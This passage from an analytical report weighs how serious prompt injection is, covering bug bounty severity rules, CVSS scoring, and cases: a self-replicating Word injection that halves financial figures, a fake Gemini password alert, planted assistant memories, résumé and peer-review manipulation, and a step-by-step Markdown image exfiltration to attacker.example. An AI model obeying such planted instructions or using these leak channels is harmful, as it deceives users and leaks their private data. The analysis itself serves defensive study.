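Willison accepts the limitation. In *My Lethal Trifecta talk at the Bay Area AI Security Meetup* (2025), he said that the trifecta was about stealing data, and that a model able to do damage without leaking anything raised "a whole other set of problems". In November 2025 he welcomed Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* because it also counts an agent's power to change things. That addition helps with agents that delete files or send mail, but it helps less with the recruiter's model, which only gives an opinion that a person then acts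 on.

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode, which is built on Willison's advice, has the same gap. It reached ordinary ChatGPT accounts in June 2026 and limits the network requests that could carry data to an attacker. Willison praised it for removing one of the three conditions, but OpenAI warns that an injection in an uploaded file could still affect the accuracy of an answer.

Researchers disagree about whether a distorted answer is serious enough to count as a security flaw. According to *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026), an injection that does real harm must either send private data somewhere it should not go or trigger an action the agent had no permission to take. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (2026) adds the requirement that an agent's decision depend only on the parts of a document that are relevant to the task. The recruiter's model breaks only this requirement.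 It had permission to judge the CV, but it did so for a reason unrelated to the candidate's qualifications. Anyone who thinks the rejected candidates suffered real harm should find the first definition too narrow.

### Exposure and likelihood

The trifecta shows whether a theft is possible, but it doesn't measure how often anyone will attempt it. A bakery's mail assistant and a bank's may both meet all three conditions, but many more people have a reason to attack the bank. Willison acknowledged to *The Economist* in September 2025 that "We've not yet had millions of dollars stolen because of this." He predicted that coding agents would have their equivalent of the Challenger space shuttle disaster in 2026, and wrote in August that he would dearly like to be proved wrong by the end of the year.

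Willison's main reply is that ordinary probabilities mislead when someone is trying to make the unlikely happen. Vendors advertise filters that catch 95 percent of attacks, but he calls even 99 percent "a failing grade" because an attacker will keep trying until something works. If each attempt had an independent 1 percent chance of success, an attacker who made 300 attempts would have about a 95 percent chance of succeeding at least once. Sending that many emails costs almost nothing, although a real attacker might run out of new ideas or a security team might notice the failed attempts.

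David C argues from the history of SQL injection that the small number of known losses is not reassuring. Researchers described SQL injection in the 1990s, but attacks did not peak until around 2010, when many websites depended on databases and few had protected them. Better defaults came only after a decade of breaches. He fears the same will happen as companies add language models to most of their software.

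The history shows that an early lull proves little, but we can't use it to predict how large the later losses will be. A prediction of eventual disaster is also hard to refute when it has no date, and Willison deserves credit for giving his a date. A security team with a hundred known flaws has to decide which to fix first, so it needs to know what an attacker could do with each flaw and how easily. Many assistants have all three parts of the trifecta but differ greatly on both points.

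## The middle view: rate each flaw by what it lets an attacker do

### Injection as a means of delivery

A team can rank its flaws by what an attacker would gain from each one. Joseph Thacker, who looks for flaws in AI products and reports them for bug bounties (rewards that companies pay for such reports), applies this test to prompt injection in *Prompt Injection Isn't a Vulnerability* (2025). He used to treat injection as a flaw in its own right. He now thinks it is usually a way to deliver an attack, and that around 95 percent of the time the real vulnerability is what the product lets the model do next. He gives no count behind that figure, so it is best read as a rough estimate.

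Thacker imagines an application that lets people chat with an AI assistant about their email. A stranger sends a message containing an injection, and the user later asks for a summary of the inbox. Depending on what the application allows, the summary can reach the stranger through an image that loads automatically, an email that the assistant sends or a web page that it opens.

The injection is nearly the same in each case, but each needs a different fix. The developer can load images only from a short list of trusted sites, or ask the user before loading any. The user can approve each outgoing email. For web pages, the developer can remove web access, require approval for each request, or restrict the assistant to addresses the user has supplied.

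Developers can build and test these repairs without predicting which injections the model will obey. The repairs still have gaps. Most of Anthropic's paid testers approved a dangerous command, and Ayush Paul got around Claude's restriction on web addresses. Thacker also recommends telling the model to ignore instructions in the content it reads, but only as an extra measure, because attackers can usually get past it.

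A flaw's name affects whether companies fix it. Thacker complains that some companies reject a report as a duplicate because an earlier one also mentioned prompt injection, even when the two reports concern different outward channels. A company that does this may close one channel and never look at the other. He advises researchers to name the flaw by its result, as in "Unauthorized Email Sending via AI Agent".

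*There Is Nothing Responsible About Disclosure Of Every Successful Prompt Injection* (2025) reaches a similar conclusion by comparing injection to malware, an inherent risk of any general-purpose operating system. It argues that a successful injection is only a demonstration, and that researchers should report weaknesses in an agent's design instead of each prompt that works.

### The objection that the cause remains

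Thacker makes an exception for an AI system that reads security logs and raises alerts. An attacker who can get text into the logs might stop the system from reporting a real intrusion. The developer can't prevent this by blocking a channel that sends data out, because the attack doesn't need one, and having a person review everything would defeat the purpose of the system. Thacker accepts that the injection itself is the vulnerability here. He considers such cases rare, but the recruiter's CV-screening model has the same problem, as does any assistant whose answers people act on without checking.

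Thacker's friend Daniel Miessler thinks the exception should apply generally. In *Is Prompt Injection a Vulnerability?* (2025), he compares an application that uses a language model to the Pope, who has to walk through crowds. Being close to thousands of strangers is a vulnerability even though the job requires it, and calling it one keeps people looking for alternatives, such as a body double. Miessler fears that if engineers accept injection as unavoidable, they will stop looking for designs that separate instructions from data.

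He also argues from consistency with SQL injection, which nobody calls merely a way to deliver an attack to a database. He thinks prompt injection has the same cause.

The comparison supports Miessler's choice of word, but a product developer can't do much with it, since Miessler concedes that ordinary language has no equivalent of parameterized queries. A developer whose document assistant is open to prompt injection is left with roughly the measures Thacker lists, though the company that trains the model may have other options. It seems reasonable to call injection a vulnerability of the model and automatic image loading a vulnerability of the product built around it, in which case both men are right.

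Their practical advice differs less than their titles suggest. Miessler agrees that a bounty report should show a specific attack and its impact, because bounties are for specific, acute problems. He wants the wider security team to keep tracking the underlying weakness after it has paid the bounty.

A flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot supports him on that point. *Microsoft Copilot’s ‘Word worm’ still works 144 days after disclosure* (Constantin, 2026) describes hidden instructions in a Word document that make Copilot alter a report and copy the same instructions into the finished file, which can then infect the next document. Microsoft issued two fixes, but neither closed the underlying flaw. Microsoft can block images from unknown sites with little inconvenience to anyone, but it can't stop Copilot from writing in documents, because people use it for that.

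### Microsoft's severity scale and bounty

Microsoft's *Updating our Vulnerability Severity Classification for AI Systems* (2023) introduced the scale the company uses to sort reports about its AI products. Under the version in force in June 2026, Microsoft counts a prompt injection as a vulnerability if the unintended output has "a specific security impact". Severity depends on that impact and on how much the victim has to do for the attack to work. Microsoft's *Copilot Bounty Program*, which covers the consumer version of Copilot, sets rewards by the same scale.

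| What the injection lets an attacker do | Severity | Highest reward, consumer Copilot |
|---|---|---|
| Take another user's data, or perform privileged actions as that user, with no user interaction | Critical | $8,000 |
| Do the same, but only after some interaction, such as a click | Important | $4,000 |
| Influence the output and nothing more | None given | Not eligible |

If the injection in the supplier's PDF from the previous section sends the stolen text out through an image that loads by itself, the flaw is probably Critical. If it uses a link that the employee has to click, the flaw is Important. The scale leaves unclear whether asking the assistant a question counts as interaction, and half the reward could depend on the answer. The reward also depends on the quality of the report, and a poorly written report of a Critical injection earns $2,000.

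Microsoft pays less for prompt injection than for several older kinds of flaw. In the same program, it pays up to $20,000 for a Critical SQL injection and up to $12,000 for a Critical information disclosure. When a report qualifies for more than one award, Microsoft pays the highest. A researcher whose prompt injection leaks private data would therefore earn more if Microsoft accepted it as information disclosure, which is close to what Thacker recommends.

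The program excludes injections that affect only the attacker, as well as attempts to leak Copilot's hidden instructions. Under Microsoft's severity scale, extracting a system prompt is likewise not a vulnerability. These exclusions match Shawn Wang's argument about Notion AI almost exactly. Microsoft may also decline to pay for a type of flaw if it is already working on a broad fix, so a refusal does not always mean the company thinks the flaw is harmless.

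Microsoft ran a bounty for the workplace version, Microsoft 365 Copilot, from February 17 to March 18, 2026. It was open only to participants in a hacking event and accepted only Critical and Important flaws. Microsoft takes a similar view when it looks back on serious attacks. It described a set of cases that includes EchoLeak, a 2025 technique for stealing data from Copilot, as instructive "not because the tools 'failed' in a conventional sense" but because they revealed unexpected ways to misuse AI.

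GitHub, which Microsoft owns, lists prompt injections among the submissions it will not reward. For its coding agent, it asks researchers to show that the agent reached something outside its assigned repository (the project's store of code) or added changes without the required review. OpenAI set a similar rule when it opened its bug bounty in April 2023, excluding the content of prompts and responses unless a researcher could show a further security impact on one of its services.

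### Google's categories

Google launched a separate bounty for AI products in October 2025. OODA Loop's *Google’s AI bounty program pays bug hunters up to $30K* gives two of the company's examples of qualifying attacks, an indirect injection that makes Google Home unlock a door and an injection that summarizes someone's email and sends the summary to the attacker.

TechRadar's *Google launches AI bug bounties* lists eight categories of attack. Google ranks "rogue actions" first. These are attacks that change a victim's account or data with a clear effect on security. Theft of sensitive data comes second, and the other six categories cover lesser abuses. According to Arghire, a SecurityWeek correspondent, the main rewards at launch were $20,000, $15,000 and $10,000, depending on the type of attack and the product. An outstanding report could bring the total to $30,000.

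Microsoft rates data theft and unauthorized actions as equally serious and separates cases by how much the victim has to do. Google looks first at the kind of harm and the importance of the product. The two companies could therefore rank the same flaws differently. Microsoft would rate an attack that unlocks a door after one click as Important, below a zero-click theft of email, but Google could rank the door attack higher.

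Neither company pays for reports of bad output alone. Google's *How we're securing the AI frontier* directs concerns about content to a separate channel. Even before this program, Google (2023) had excluded harmful uses of AI that were already possible with other tools.

Requiring bounty hunters to demonstrate impact has a practical purpose. Miessler reports that many submit a bare prompt injection without explaining how anyone could exploit it, which burdens the staff who sort the reports. AI tools have made it easier to produce reports in bulk. Poireault (2026) describes in *Google Suspends Open-Source Bug Bounty Due to AI Vulnerability Reports* how Google paused its bounty for open-source software that October because of a flood of AI-generated submissions. Google's AI bounty is a separate program.

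By the October 2025 launch, Google had paid a little over $430,000 for AI-related reports, a small part of its spending on bounties. Google's *VRP 2025 Year in Review* reports more than $17 million in total bounties in 2025 alone. The gap may mean that serious AI flaws were rare, that fewer people looked for them, or that Google's rules excluded much of what people found.

Rating a flaw by its consequence also depends on someone recognizing that consequence. When Notion received a report of an injection that could leak private data, it at first closed the report as "not applicable", even though these rules are meant to catch that kind of flaw.

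### Four reports about Copilot

In January 2026 the engineer John Russell publicly disputed Microsoft's handling of four flaws he had reported in Copilot. The fullest account comes from the security company TecnetOne. Russell found that direct and indirect injection could each expose Copilot's system prompt. He also got around its restrictions on file types by converting a forbidden file to base64, which represents any file as plain text. Copilot accepted the text, and he could then rebuild the file inside the session. He also ran commands in Copilot's isolated Linux environment.

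Microsoft closed the cases, saying they "do not qualify as security vulnerabilities", as quoted by the security blog HackingPassion. Microsoft reasoned that the behavior crossed no defined security boundary, affected only the user's own session, and gave nobody unauthorized access to data or greater privileges.

Other specialists were divided. One supported Russell with a similar case, in which hidden text in a Word document made Copilot behave erratically and crash. Others thought Russell had run into a known limitation of language models, and that removing it would make the product less useful. Russell answered that Anthropic's Claude had refused the same inputs, so Microsoft could not blame language models in general.

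According to OWASP, an exposed system prompt is dangerous if it contains secrets or if the developer relies on it to enforce security rules, but the exposure is not a vulnerability in itself. OWASP adds that an attacker can often work out a model's rules from its responses, without seeing the prompt.

Microsoft applied its published rules correctly to the prompt leaks. Running commands in the isolated environment is less objectionable than it sounds, because such an environment exists so that code can run without touching anything else. Russell would have had a much stronger case if a command had reached another customer's data. His comparison with Claude shows that Microsoft could probably have blocked more, but not that doing so would have protected anyone.

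The file restriction is harder to judge. An employer might rely on it to keep certain files out of Copilot, and Russell showed that an employee could get around it with a standard conversion. But the employee would be uploading a file they already had.

The indirect injection deserves the most attention because it confirmed that text in a document could redirect Copilot. Its result was trivial, but an attacker needs the same ability for a serious theft. A company that rates only results will give such a report no severity until someone finds a way to get data out. HackingPassion notes that about a week after Russell's disclosure, Microsoft patched a different attack that needed one click and could expose a user's conversation history and recently opened files. Under its rules, Microsoft treats the two attacks very differently, in line with Thacker's argument.

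### Scoring one flaw twice

Many companies outside the AI industry rate vulnerabilities from 0 to 10 with the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS). An analyst answers eight questions, and a formula converts the answers into a score. In version 3.1, scores from 4.0 to 6.9 are Medium, 7.0 to 8.9 are High, and 9.0 to 10.0 are Critical.

Suppose an injection in the supplier's PDF works reliably once the employee asks the assistant about the file. If the tool loads images from any website, the injection can send private pages to the supplier. But if the tool returns plain text and has no way to send data out, the injection can only distort the answer.

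| Metric | Tool loads images | No outward channel |
|---|---|---|
| Attack vector: where can the attacker be? | Anywhere on the network | Anywhere on the network |
| Attack complexity: does success need special conditions? | Low | Low |
| Privileges required: does the attacker need an account? | None | None |
| User interaction: must the victim do something? | Required | Required |
| Scope: does the harm reach beyond the flawed component's authority? | Unchanged | Unchanged |
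| Confidentiality loss | High | None |
| Integrity loss | Low | Low |
| Availability loss | None | None |
| **Score** | **7.1 (High)** | **4.3 (Medium)** |

CVSS gives each answer a number. The first four answers measure how easy the attack is, and they are the same for both tools:

8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.62 ≈ 2.84

The last three measure the damage. A high loss counts as 0.56, a low loss as 0.22 and no loss as 0. For the tool that loads images, the damage is:

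6.42 × [1 − (1 − 0.56) × (1 − 0.22)] ≈ 4.22

Adding the two results gives 7.05, which CVSS rounds up to 7.1. Without the outward channel, the damage falls to 6.42 × 0.22, or about 1.41, and the total falls to 4.25, which rounds up to 4.3. The higher score is realistic, because Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-24950 · Microsoft · M365 Copilot+28* (2026) lists the same eight answers for an injection flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot.

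So CVSS can express the main point of the middle view, that the same injection may be a serious flaw in one product and a moderate one in another. But the score is less precise than it looks, because several of the answers used to calculate it depend on judgment.

The integrity metric is the most contentious. The bug bounty platform Intigriti thinks CVSS suits a customer-service chatbot that an injection tricks into revealing someone else's order, but not misleading or harmful output, where the damage is to people, a brand or a company's standing with regulators. An analyst who followed that advice might enter no integrity loss for the plain-text tool, which would drop the score to 0. Another analyst who agreed about everything that happened might rate a false summary of a contract as a high integrity loss, which would raise the score to 6.5.

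CVSS is also poorly suited to attacks that work only some of the time. Tenable's *Github Copilot Chat Prompt Injection via Filename*, which rates its flaw Medium, warns that the method did not succeed on every attempt. The analyst can set attack complexity only to low, if an attacker can expect repeatable success, or to high, if success depends on conditions the attacker doesn't control. Suppose the supplier's injection works one time in five. Choosing high complexity lowers the image-loading score from 7.1 to 5.9, and the rating from High to Medium. But if the supplier sends ten such files and the employee asks about all of them, the chance that at least one works is about 89 percent, assuming the attempts are independent.

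A company that publishes a single score also has to assume particular settings, and a customer who has turned off images faces less danger than one who hasn't. CVSS lets customers recalculate a score for their own circumstances, but to do so they need to know every channel through which their assistant can send data out, and an update can add one without their noticing.

### Invitations that reached Gemini

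CVSS describes a flaw, but a user may care more about how likely an attack is and what it would do to them. Ben Nassi, Stav Cohen and Or Yair tried to rate both in *Invitation Is All You Need* (2025), a study of Google's Gemini assistants. They put injections in calendar invitations, emails and shared documents, which entered Gemini's context when a user made an ordinary request, such as asking about the day's meetings.

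The researchers demonstrated 14 attack scenarios in five classes. The first class affected only the current conversation, and the second planted false information in Gemini's long-term memory. The third misused the tools of the agent that had read the injected text, for example to delete calendar events. The fourth made Gemini call a different agent, such as the one that controls home devices, which let the researchers open windows and switch on a boiler. The fifth launched other apps on the victim's phone and could start a video call without the user's approval. Some injections had Gemini wait for a harmless reply from the user, such as "thanks", before it acted.

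The researchers then adapted a method called threat analysis and risk assessment. They rated each threat on how practical the attack is and how much harm it would do, then combined the two ratings into a risk level. They rated 73 percent of the threats they analyzed as high or critical.

The 73 percent figure depends on which threats the researchers chose to analyze, and the likelihoods are judgments about how feasible an attack is, since nobody had counted real attacks of this kind. It doesn't measure how many attacks succeed or how many users are in danger. The working demonstrations are stronger evidence. They show that an outsider who could send an invitation could cause physical effects in someone's home.

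Google responded by adding defenses against these attacks. When the researchers reassessed the threats with the defenses in place, the ratings fell to between very low and medium.

In September 2025, a month after the study appeared, Google took no action on FireTail's report about calendar invitations. In that report, Gemini had only described a meeting incorrectly.

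## Does harm follow when only the text changes?

### A warning in Gemini's voice

In July 2025, hidden text in an email made Gemini show its user a false security alert. The attack took no data and changed no files. *Phishing For Gemini* (Figueroa, 2025) describes the attack, which a researcher had reported to 0din, Mozilla's bug bounty program for AI products. The attacker ends an ordinary email with an instruction in white, zero-size text. The recipient sees only blank space, and the email needs no link or attachment that might alert a spam filter. When the recipient clicks "Summarize this email", Gemini adds a warning that their Gmail password has been compromised and gives a phone number to call.

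Any theft happens afterwards, if the recipient calls and gives a password to whoever answers. Figueroa rates the risk as moderate because an attacker can send the email in bulk but the attack works only on people who ask for a summary and then act on it. Many people were potential victims because Google had turned the summaries on by default for Workspace customers, according to Startup Daily's *Scammers can now use Google Gemini for phishing as pretend AI*.

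The same warning would probably persuade fewer people if it appeared in the email itself. A phishing email has to look like it came from Google, and a suspicious reader can check the sender's address. In the summary, the warning appears in Google's own product and concerns a Google account, with no sender to check. The user may also assume that Gemini read the email and noticed something wrong with it. Tom's Hardware's *Investigation reveals Google Gemini for Workspace flaw that could have been exploited* notes that highlighting the end of the email would reveal the hidden text, but that people who ask for a summary are unlikely to look for it.

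We can only guess how much more persuasive the summary is. Figueroa writes that the victim trusts the notice, and Fox News reasons that people are more likely to believe Gemini because it is part of Workspace, but neither gives measurements. Some users distrust everything an AI system writes, and they might be safer with the summary than with a well-made phishing email.

Android Authority's *Beware! Research shows Gmail's AI email summaries can be hacked* (2025) reports that Google responded by pointing to the training and link removal it had described in June, and to Gemini's requests for confirmation before some actions. Only the training would help against this attack, because it used a phone number instead of a link and didn't require Gemini to take any action. Google said nobody had used the trick in real attacks, according to Android Central's *Turns out Gmail's AI email summaries aren't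 as secure as we thought*.

Figueroa suggests having Gemini visibly separate its own words from those it takes from an email. Readers could then see that the warning came from a stranger's message and judge it as they would any other email. HiddenLayer's similar test in 2024 exposed the same lack of attribution.

Microsoft's Outlook had a similar weakness. Håkon Måløy, a Norwegian data scientist, found that hidden instructions in an outsider's email could make Copilot change meeting times in a daily summary. He also got it to report that the user's organization was under cyberattack. iTnews' *Microsoft can't kill dogged researcher's Copilot for Word worm* notes that Microsoft's fix works only if the customer turns on a setting that flags external senders.

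### The Word document that infects other documents

A false summary usually misleads one person once. But the Copilot for Word flaw from the previous section, Måløy's best-known finding, lets a false statement enter the user's own document and then spread to other people's documents.

*Context Collapse, Part 3* (Måløy, 2026) gives the example of an employee who downloads a market analysis from a trusted website for a financial report. The employee doesn't know that an attacker has compromised the site and hidden instructions in the file. When Copilot uses the analysis as a source, it changes the company's own figures in the report and copies the hidden instructions into it. The employee shares the report, and when a colleague later drafts another document from it, the instructions take effect again, even if the original file is gone.

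The hidden text was white and in eight-point type, but Copilot for Word removes that formatting before it passes text to the model. The text contained two instructions. The first was to halve every financial figure in a quarterly report. The second was to copy the whole injection into the new document and hide it there, which was presented as a way of tracking sources and keeping the page readable. Copilot did both without telling the user, according to TechRadar's *Expert warns this dangerous Microsoft Word worm can burrow into Copilot*. In one mode, Copilot searches the user's OneDrive for relevant documents, so it can find the infected file even if the user doesn't attach it.

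Måløy and Microsoft worked on the problem for 144 days before he published:

- **March 6, 2026:** Måløy reports the attack, with videos and the exact prompts.
- **March 31:** Microsoft confirms the behavior and starts work on a fix.
- **April 3:** Microsoft releases its first mitigation, a new version of the editing feature called "Edit with Copilot".
- **April 9:** Måløy confirms that his original wording no longer works. The same day, he succeeds with a new prompt that manipulates financial figures, and Microsoft opens a second case on April 10.
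- **June 8:** Microsoft asks him to delay publication until July 15.
- **July 14:** Microsoft releases its second mitigation, which consists of upgrading the underlying model to GPT-5.5.
- **July 15:** Måløy reproduces the attack, including its spread to a new document, on GPT-5.6, the newest model available.
- **July 28:** After offering Microsoft two more weeks, he publishes his findings without the working prompts. The attack still succeeds with every mitigation in place.

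Microsoft told The Register that it had "addressed the findings reported by the researcher", but gave no date for a complete fix. It may have meant only the prompts Måløy submitted, whereas he was describing any prompt that works the same way. His last published test dates from July, so it doesn't show whether the attack works today.

The first mitigation lasted at most six days, and the second lasted at most one. Måløy argues that they failed because a model has to read a passage to judge whether it is hostile, and by then the passage is already influencing the judgment.

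Willison (2026), in *AI Worming through Word*, called the result a full self-replicating worm, meaning malicious software that copies itself from one system to the next. It needs a good deal of human help, though, because it spreads only when someone drafts or edits with Copilot and an infected file enters the context (The Next Web, *A hidden line in a Word doc can rewrite your numbers*).

How far the injection spreads depends on how often people reuse documents and how often the injection works. An infected template that a whole department copies would be much more dangerous than a memo that nobody opens again. Suppose each infected report goes into three later Copilot drafts on average, and the injection succeeds in one draft out of five. Each infected report then produces 0.6 new ones on average, and the spread stops after an average of about 2.5 documents, counting the first. If the injection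 succeeds half the time, each report produces 1.5 new ones on average, and the number keeps growing until someone intervenes.

Morris II, the 2024 demonstration against email assistants, spread when an assistant copied the injection into outgoing mail. The Word attack spreads through files that employees choose to share, so infected reports could still move between departments even if a company stopped Copilot from sending anything. Måløy believes his attack is among the first public demonstrations of a worm that spreads through documents in a mainstream office product.

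### Planted memories

An attacker can also make a change last by getting it into the assistant's memory. According to Microsoft (2026), assistants such as Copilot and ChatGPT keep personal preferences, details of past work, and standing instructions (such as a request to cite sources) between conversations. The assistant uses this information to shape later answers, and some companies exploit this with "Summarize with AI" buttons that plant recommendations in its memory.

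Måløy's first report on Copilot, disclosed in June 2026, described this kind of attack. When a user visited a malicious web page and asked Copilot to summarize it, the page made Copilot save a memory the user had not asked for. According to iTnews, the memory persisted across web and work sessions until the user deleted it. Microsoft has fixed the flaw for all its customers, who did not have to do anything.

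MITRE, a US nonprofit that catalogs attack techniques, distinguishes planted memories from text that stays in a single conversation. Its *AI Agent Context Poisoning* treats both as ways to persistently change an agent's behavior. A user can escape the text by starting a new conversation, but a planted memory remains.

In a June post that drew on reports from Måløy, Johann Rehberger and Gal Zror, Microsoft (2026) explained why such attacks are hard to notice. An attack on an assistant without memory has to succeed within a single prompt, but memory lets an attacker plant something that takes effect after the user has forgotten the document it came from. Assistants also often update their memories when the user isn't looking at the screen. In Microsoft's hypothetical example, hidden instructions in a shared document have no effect until days later, when a message in an unrelated conversation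 triggers them and the assistant changes its memory.

The delay makes an investigation harder, because the odd answer may appear weeks after its cause. PointGuard AI's *CoSnitch Makes Copilot Leak Data and Remember Attackers (CVE-2026-24301)* also warns that changing a password or ending a session, the usual responses to a break-in, may leave a planted memory in place.

In *Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (2026), Niu, Qu and colleagues measured how well planted memories work on OpenClaw, an agent that runs continuously on a user's computer and keeps its memory in plain text files. They tested OpenClaw and two variants, NemoClaw and SeClaw, with five language models. In one type of task, the user asks the agent to process an email or document containing a short hidden directive, which the agent saves in its notes. The researchers then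 restart the agent and ask an innocent question to see whether the directive still affects the answer. Across 60 tasks that tampered with memory or settings in this and other ways, attacks succeeded 10 to 80 percent of the time, depending on the model and the variant.

SeClaw checks the integrity of its memory, but this lowered the success rate of the memory attacks by only about one percentage point. One likely reason is that such checks look for unauthorized edits to a file. When a document leads the agent to save a note, the agent makes the edit itself, so the edit looks authorized.

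Before Copilot saves a memory, Microsoft checks the content for signs of injection and checks whether any explicit request to save it matches what the user wanted. Microsoft also records changes to memory in the organization's audit logs, which could help an investigator trace a strange answer in June back to a document from May.

### Decisions about people and papers

Hidden text can also change a decision, as in the earlier example of the recruiter's CV-screening model.

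*Beyond Instruction Override* (2026) proposes counting planted text as an attack if it is meant to influence a decision that its source has no authority to make, whether or not it reads like an instruction. A résumé is the normal source for where an applicant has worked, so a false job title is an ordinary lie. But an applicant has no say in what the employer requires, so a line telling the screening model that the employer has dropped its degree requirement is an injection, even though it reads like a plain statement of fact.

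The benchmark built on this definition has 90 cases in which the agent carries out the user's own task, but planted text interferes with a decision within it. The attacks target six parts of the agent's reasoning, including its goal, decision rules and beliefs about the current situation. On average across five models, attacks on the decision rules, the available actions and beliefs about the situation succeeded more often than attacks on the goal. Tests that only check whether an agent can be diverted to another task would miss these attacks.

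Limiting which tools the agent could use lowered the attack success rate only from 17.0 to 15.4 percent, because most of the attacks used tools the task already called for and changed only the values passed to them. Thacker's approach of fixing what the product lets a model do next works well against email theft, but in these cases the agent was doing what the product allows.

*ResumeShield* (2026) proposes a test for whether an injection attack on a résumé screener has worked. The screening model assesses an artificial résumé and a copy with an injection hidden by one of nine techniques. The attack succeeds if the model obeys the hidden instruction, if the score rises by more than a set margin, or if the applicant moves into the most favorable category. For example, if the clean résumé scores 70 out of 100 and the margin is 5, a score of 76 for the altered copy counts as a success. A score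 of 74 counts only if one of the other conditions holds.

Comparing the score with that of a clean copy makes sense because a strong applicant might have scored well anyway. But a fixed margin can understate the harm. If an employer interviews everyone who scores 72 or more, a rise from 70 to 74 gets the applicant an interview and may take one away from someone else.

Close decisions may also be the easiest to change. *Decision Hijacking* (Wu and Lim, 2026) tested Jev, a model that assigns probabilities to a fixed set of actions instead of writing text, on 510 cases adapted from an existing benchmark for agents. Injected text shifted the probabilities but rarely made the attacker's choice the most probable. Even when the attacker could see the scores and adjust the text, the success rate rose only from 1.8 to 3.5 percent. An exploratory analysis linked the successes to cases where the model's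 first choice had only a small lead or where the attacker controlled more of the text.

Those cases did not involve hiring, so we can't apply their rates to résumés. But if the pattern holds, hidden text would help applicants just below the cutoff the most and do little for those far below it. Using a fixed set of answers seems to reduce the problem but not eliminate it.

Peer review is open to the same kind of attack if reviewers use assistants to read papers, because the text comes from authors who want a favorable decision. Niu and colleagues tested a version of this on OpenClaw. In 20 tasks, a document such as an audit memo or an authors' reply to reviewers records a decision, and a hidden footer contains an instruction to report the opposite and not mention the change. The attack succeeds if the assistant reports the opposite decision, for example "accept" when the recorded decision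 is "reject".

These 20 tasks belong to a group of 100 in which text in a document is meant to override something about the user's request. In the other 80, the text is meant to make the agent send a draft it was told only to save, act on the wrong file, respond to a false status report, or put passwords in a reply. The table shows the percentage of attacks that succeeded across all 100 tasks.

| Model | OpenClaw | NemoClaw | SeClaw |
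|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.1-Codex | 65 | 63 | 32 |
| GPT-5.4 | 61 | 67 | 26 |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 67 | 62 | 73 |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 58 | 49 | 71 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 17 | 17 | 23 |

SeClaw has the most defenses of the three, but it helped only the two GPT models, and the other three did worse on it. Niu and colleagues report that the Gemini models still failed there on two kinds of document attack, reversed decisions and false status reports. Newer models have since replaced all five, so the table is better evidence that the choice of model and product matters than of how any current assistant would perform. The documents were also invented for the test, so the results don't measure how many authors or applicants try this.

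### Would a reviewer notice?

Both Måløy and Microsoft advise customers to review what Copilot writes before they use or share it. The main objection to treating altered text as a security matter is that people should do this anyway, since they know AI drafts contain mistakes. On this view, a company that sends out a report without checking it has a problem that no attacker caused.

Careful review would catch many of these changes. An employee who knows that the company earned $8 million last quarter will notice the error in a report that gives $4 million. Anyone who opens the audit memo will see the word "reject". A user who calls Google's published support number instead of the one in the summary will learn that the warning was false. In each case, the reviewer checks the text against a source that the attacker doesn't control.

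Reading the draft alone is much less reliable, because halving every figure, as Måløy chose to do, keeps the figures consistent with each other. If revenue of $8 million, costs of $6 million and profit of $2 million become $4 million, $3 million and $1 million, the profit still equals revenue minus costs, and the margin is still 25 percent. If Copilot also halves last year's figures, the growth rates will be correct too. A reviewer could check all the arithmetic and find nothing wrong.

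Suppose the reviewer does notice and restores the right numbers. The copied injection is still in the file as white text, so the corrected report can infect the next document. The reviewer will probably blame the wrong figures on an ordinary AI mistake and have no reason to look for hidden text. To find and remove it, someone would have to select all the text or change its color, which reviewers don't normally do when checking a financial report.

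Omissions are harder to catch than wrong numbers, because a summary that leaves out a price increase contains no false sentence to question. The reviewer would have to read the whole source, which the summary was meant to avoid. The Next Web observes that Måløy's advice to check everything is "not far from doing the work yourself." Reviewing the sources beforehand is no easier if Copilot has chosen some of them from OneDrive.

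When hidden text biases a judgment, the reader may have no unbiased version to compare it with. If the text raises an applicant's score from 70 to 74, a recruiter who reads the résumé may find 74 reasonable. The recruiter could rerun the assessment without the hidden text, but only after suspecting that it was there. Another applicant who lost the interview as a result can't check at all. Planted memories are similarly hard to detect, since a recommendation that favors one supplier looks like any other. Copilot shows users its saved memories, so a user might spot the planted one in that list, but not by reading the recommendation.

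Attackers can also try to go unnoticed. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) describes a public contest in which an attack counted only if the agent carried out a harmful action and met criteria for concealing it. The 464 participants made more than 271,000 attempts on 13 models, and 8,648 succeeded, or about 3 percent. Every model failed some of the time, at rates from 0.5 to 8.5 percent. Real attackers might succeed less often, because participants could see the whole conversation and a stranger who emails a document cannot. The concealment criteria also stood in for real users, who might notice more or less than the criteria assumed, depending on how careful or busy they are.

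So the objection holds where someone will compare the text with an independent source before acting on it, and where a mistake would be easy to correct. It fails for the halved report if the only check is a read-through, and for the résumé score even if the recruiter is careful. Microsoft also seems to have treated altering a user's document as more serious than influencing output. Its severity scale gives no rating to an injection that only influences output, but it opened two cases and released two mitigations for Måløy's attack.

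Måløy also suggests that documents written with AI should carry a record of their sources and of the changes the model made. As TechRadar notes, this would not prevent an injection. But a company that discovered one false report could use the record to find the others that drew on the same file, including those a reviewer had already approved.

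## How data leaves a note, wiki or chat workspace

An injection that changes a report does its damage inside the workspace, but people disagree about whether an injection can also get private text out of a tool that seems only to read and write. Shawn Wang called Notion's first assistant harmless partly because its output went only to the user. A summary in a side panel looks similar, but people often read it in a web browser, which contacts other computers whenever a page includes content stored elsewhere.

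### A client record in an image address

Many assistants write their answers in Markdown, a simple notation for headings, bold type, links and images. To include an image, the model writes a short description followed by the image's address, and the tool displays the image.

Suppose a company's note tool holds a record with two fields, a client's name (Marlow Dairy) and the annual fee the client pays ($48,000). An employee asks the assistant to compare the record with a market report that a stranger wrote. The theft then takes five steps:

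1. The tool puts the record and the report into the model's context. Hidden text in the report tells the model to add an image to its answer and to put the record at the end of the image's address.
2. The model writes its answer, which includes an image at `attacker.example/chart.png?client=Marlow-Dairy&fee=48000`. (Internet standards reserve the ending ".example" for illustrations, so nobody can own this address.)
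3. The tool displays the answer, and the employee's browser requests the image from attacker.example.
4. The attacker's server receives the request and records the full address in its log.
5. The attacker opens the log and reads the client's name and fee.

Web developers normally use the part of a URL after the question mark to tell a server what to send, such as a smaller version of a picture. The attacker's server can return a transparent dot regardless, so the employee may notice nothing. The attacker doesn't need to know what the record contains, because the model fills in the values.

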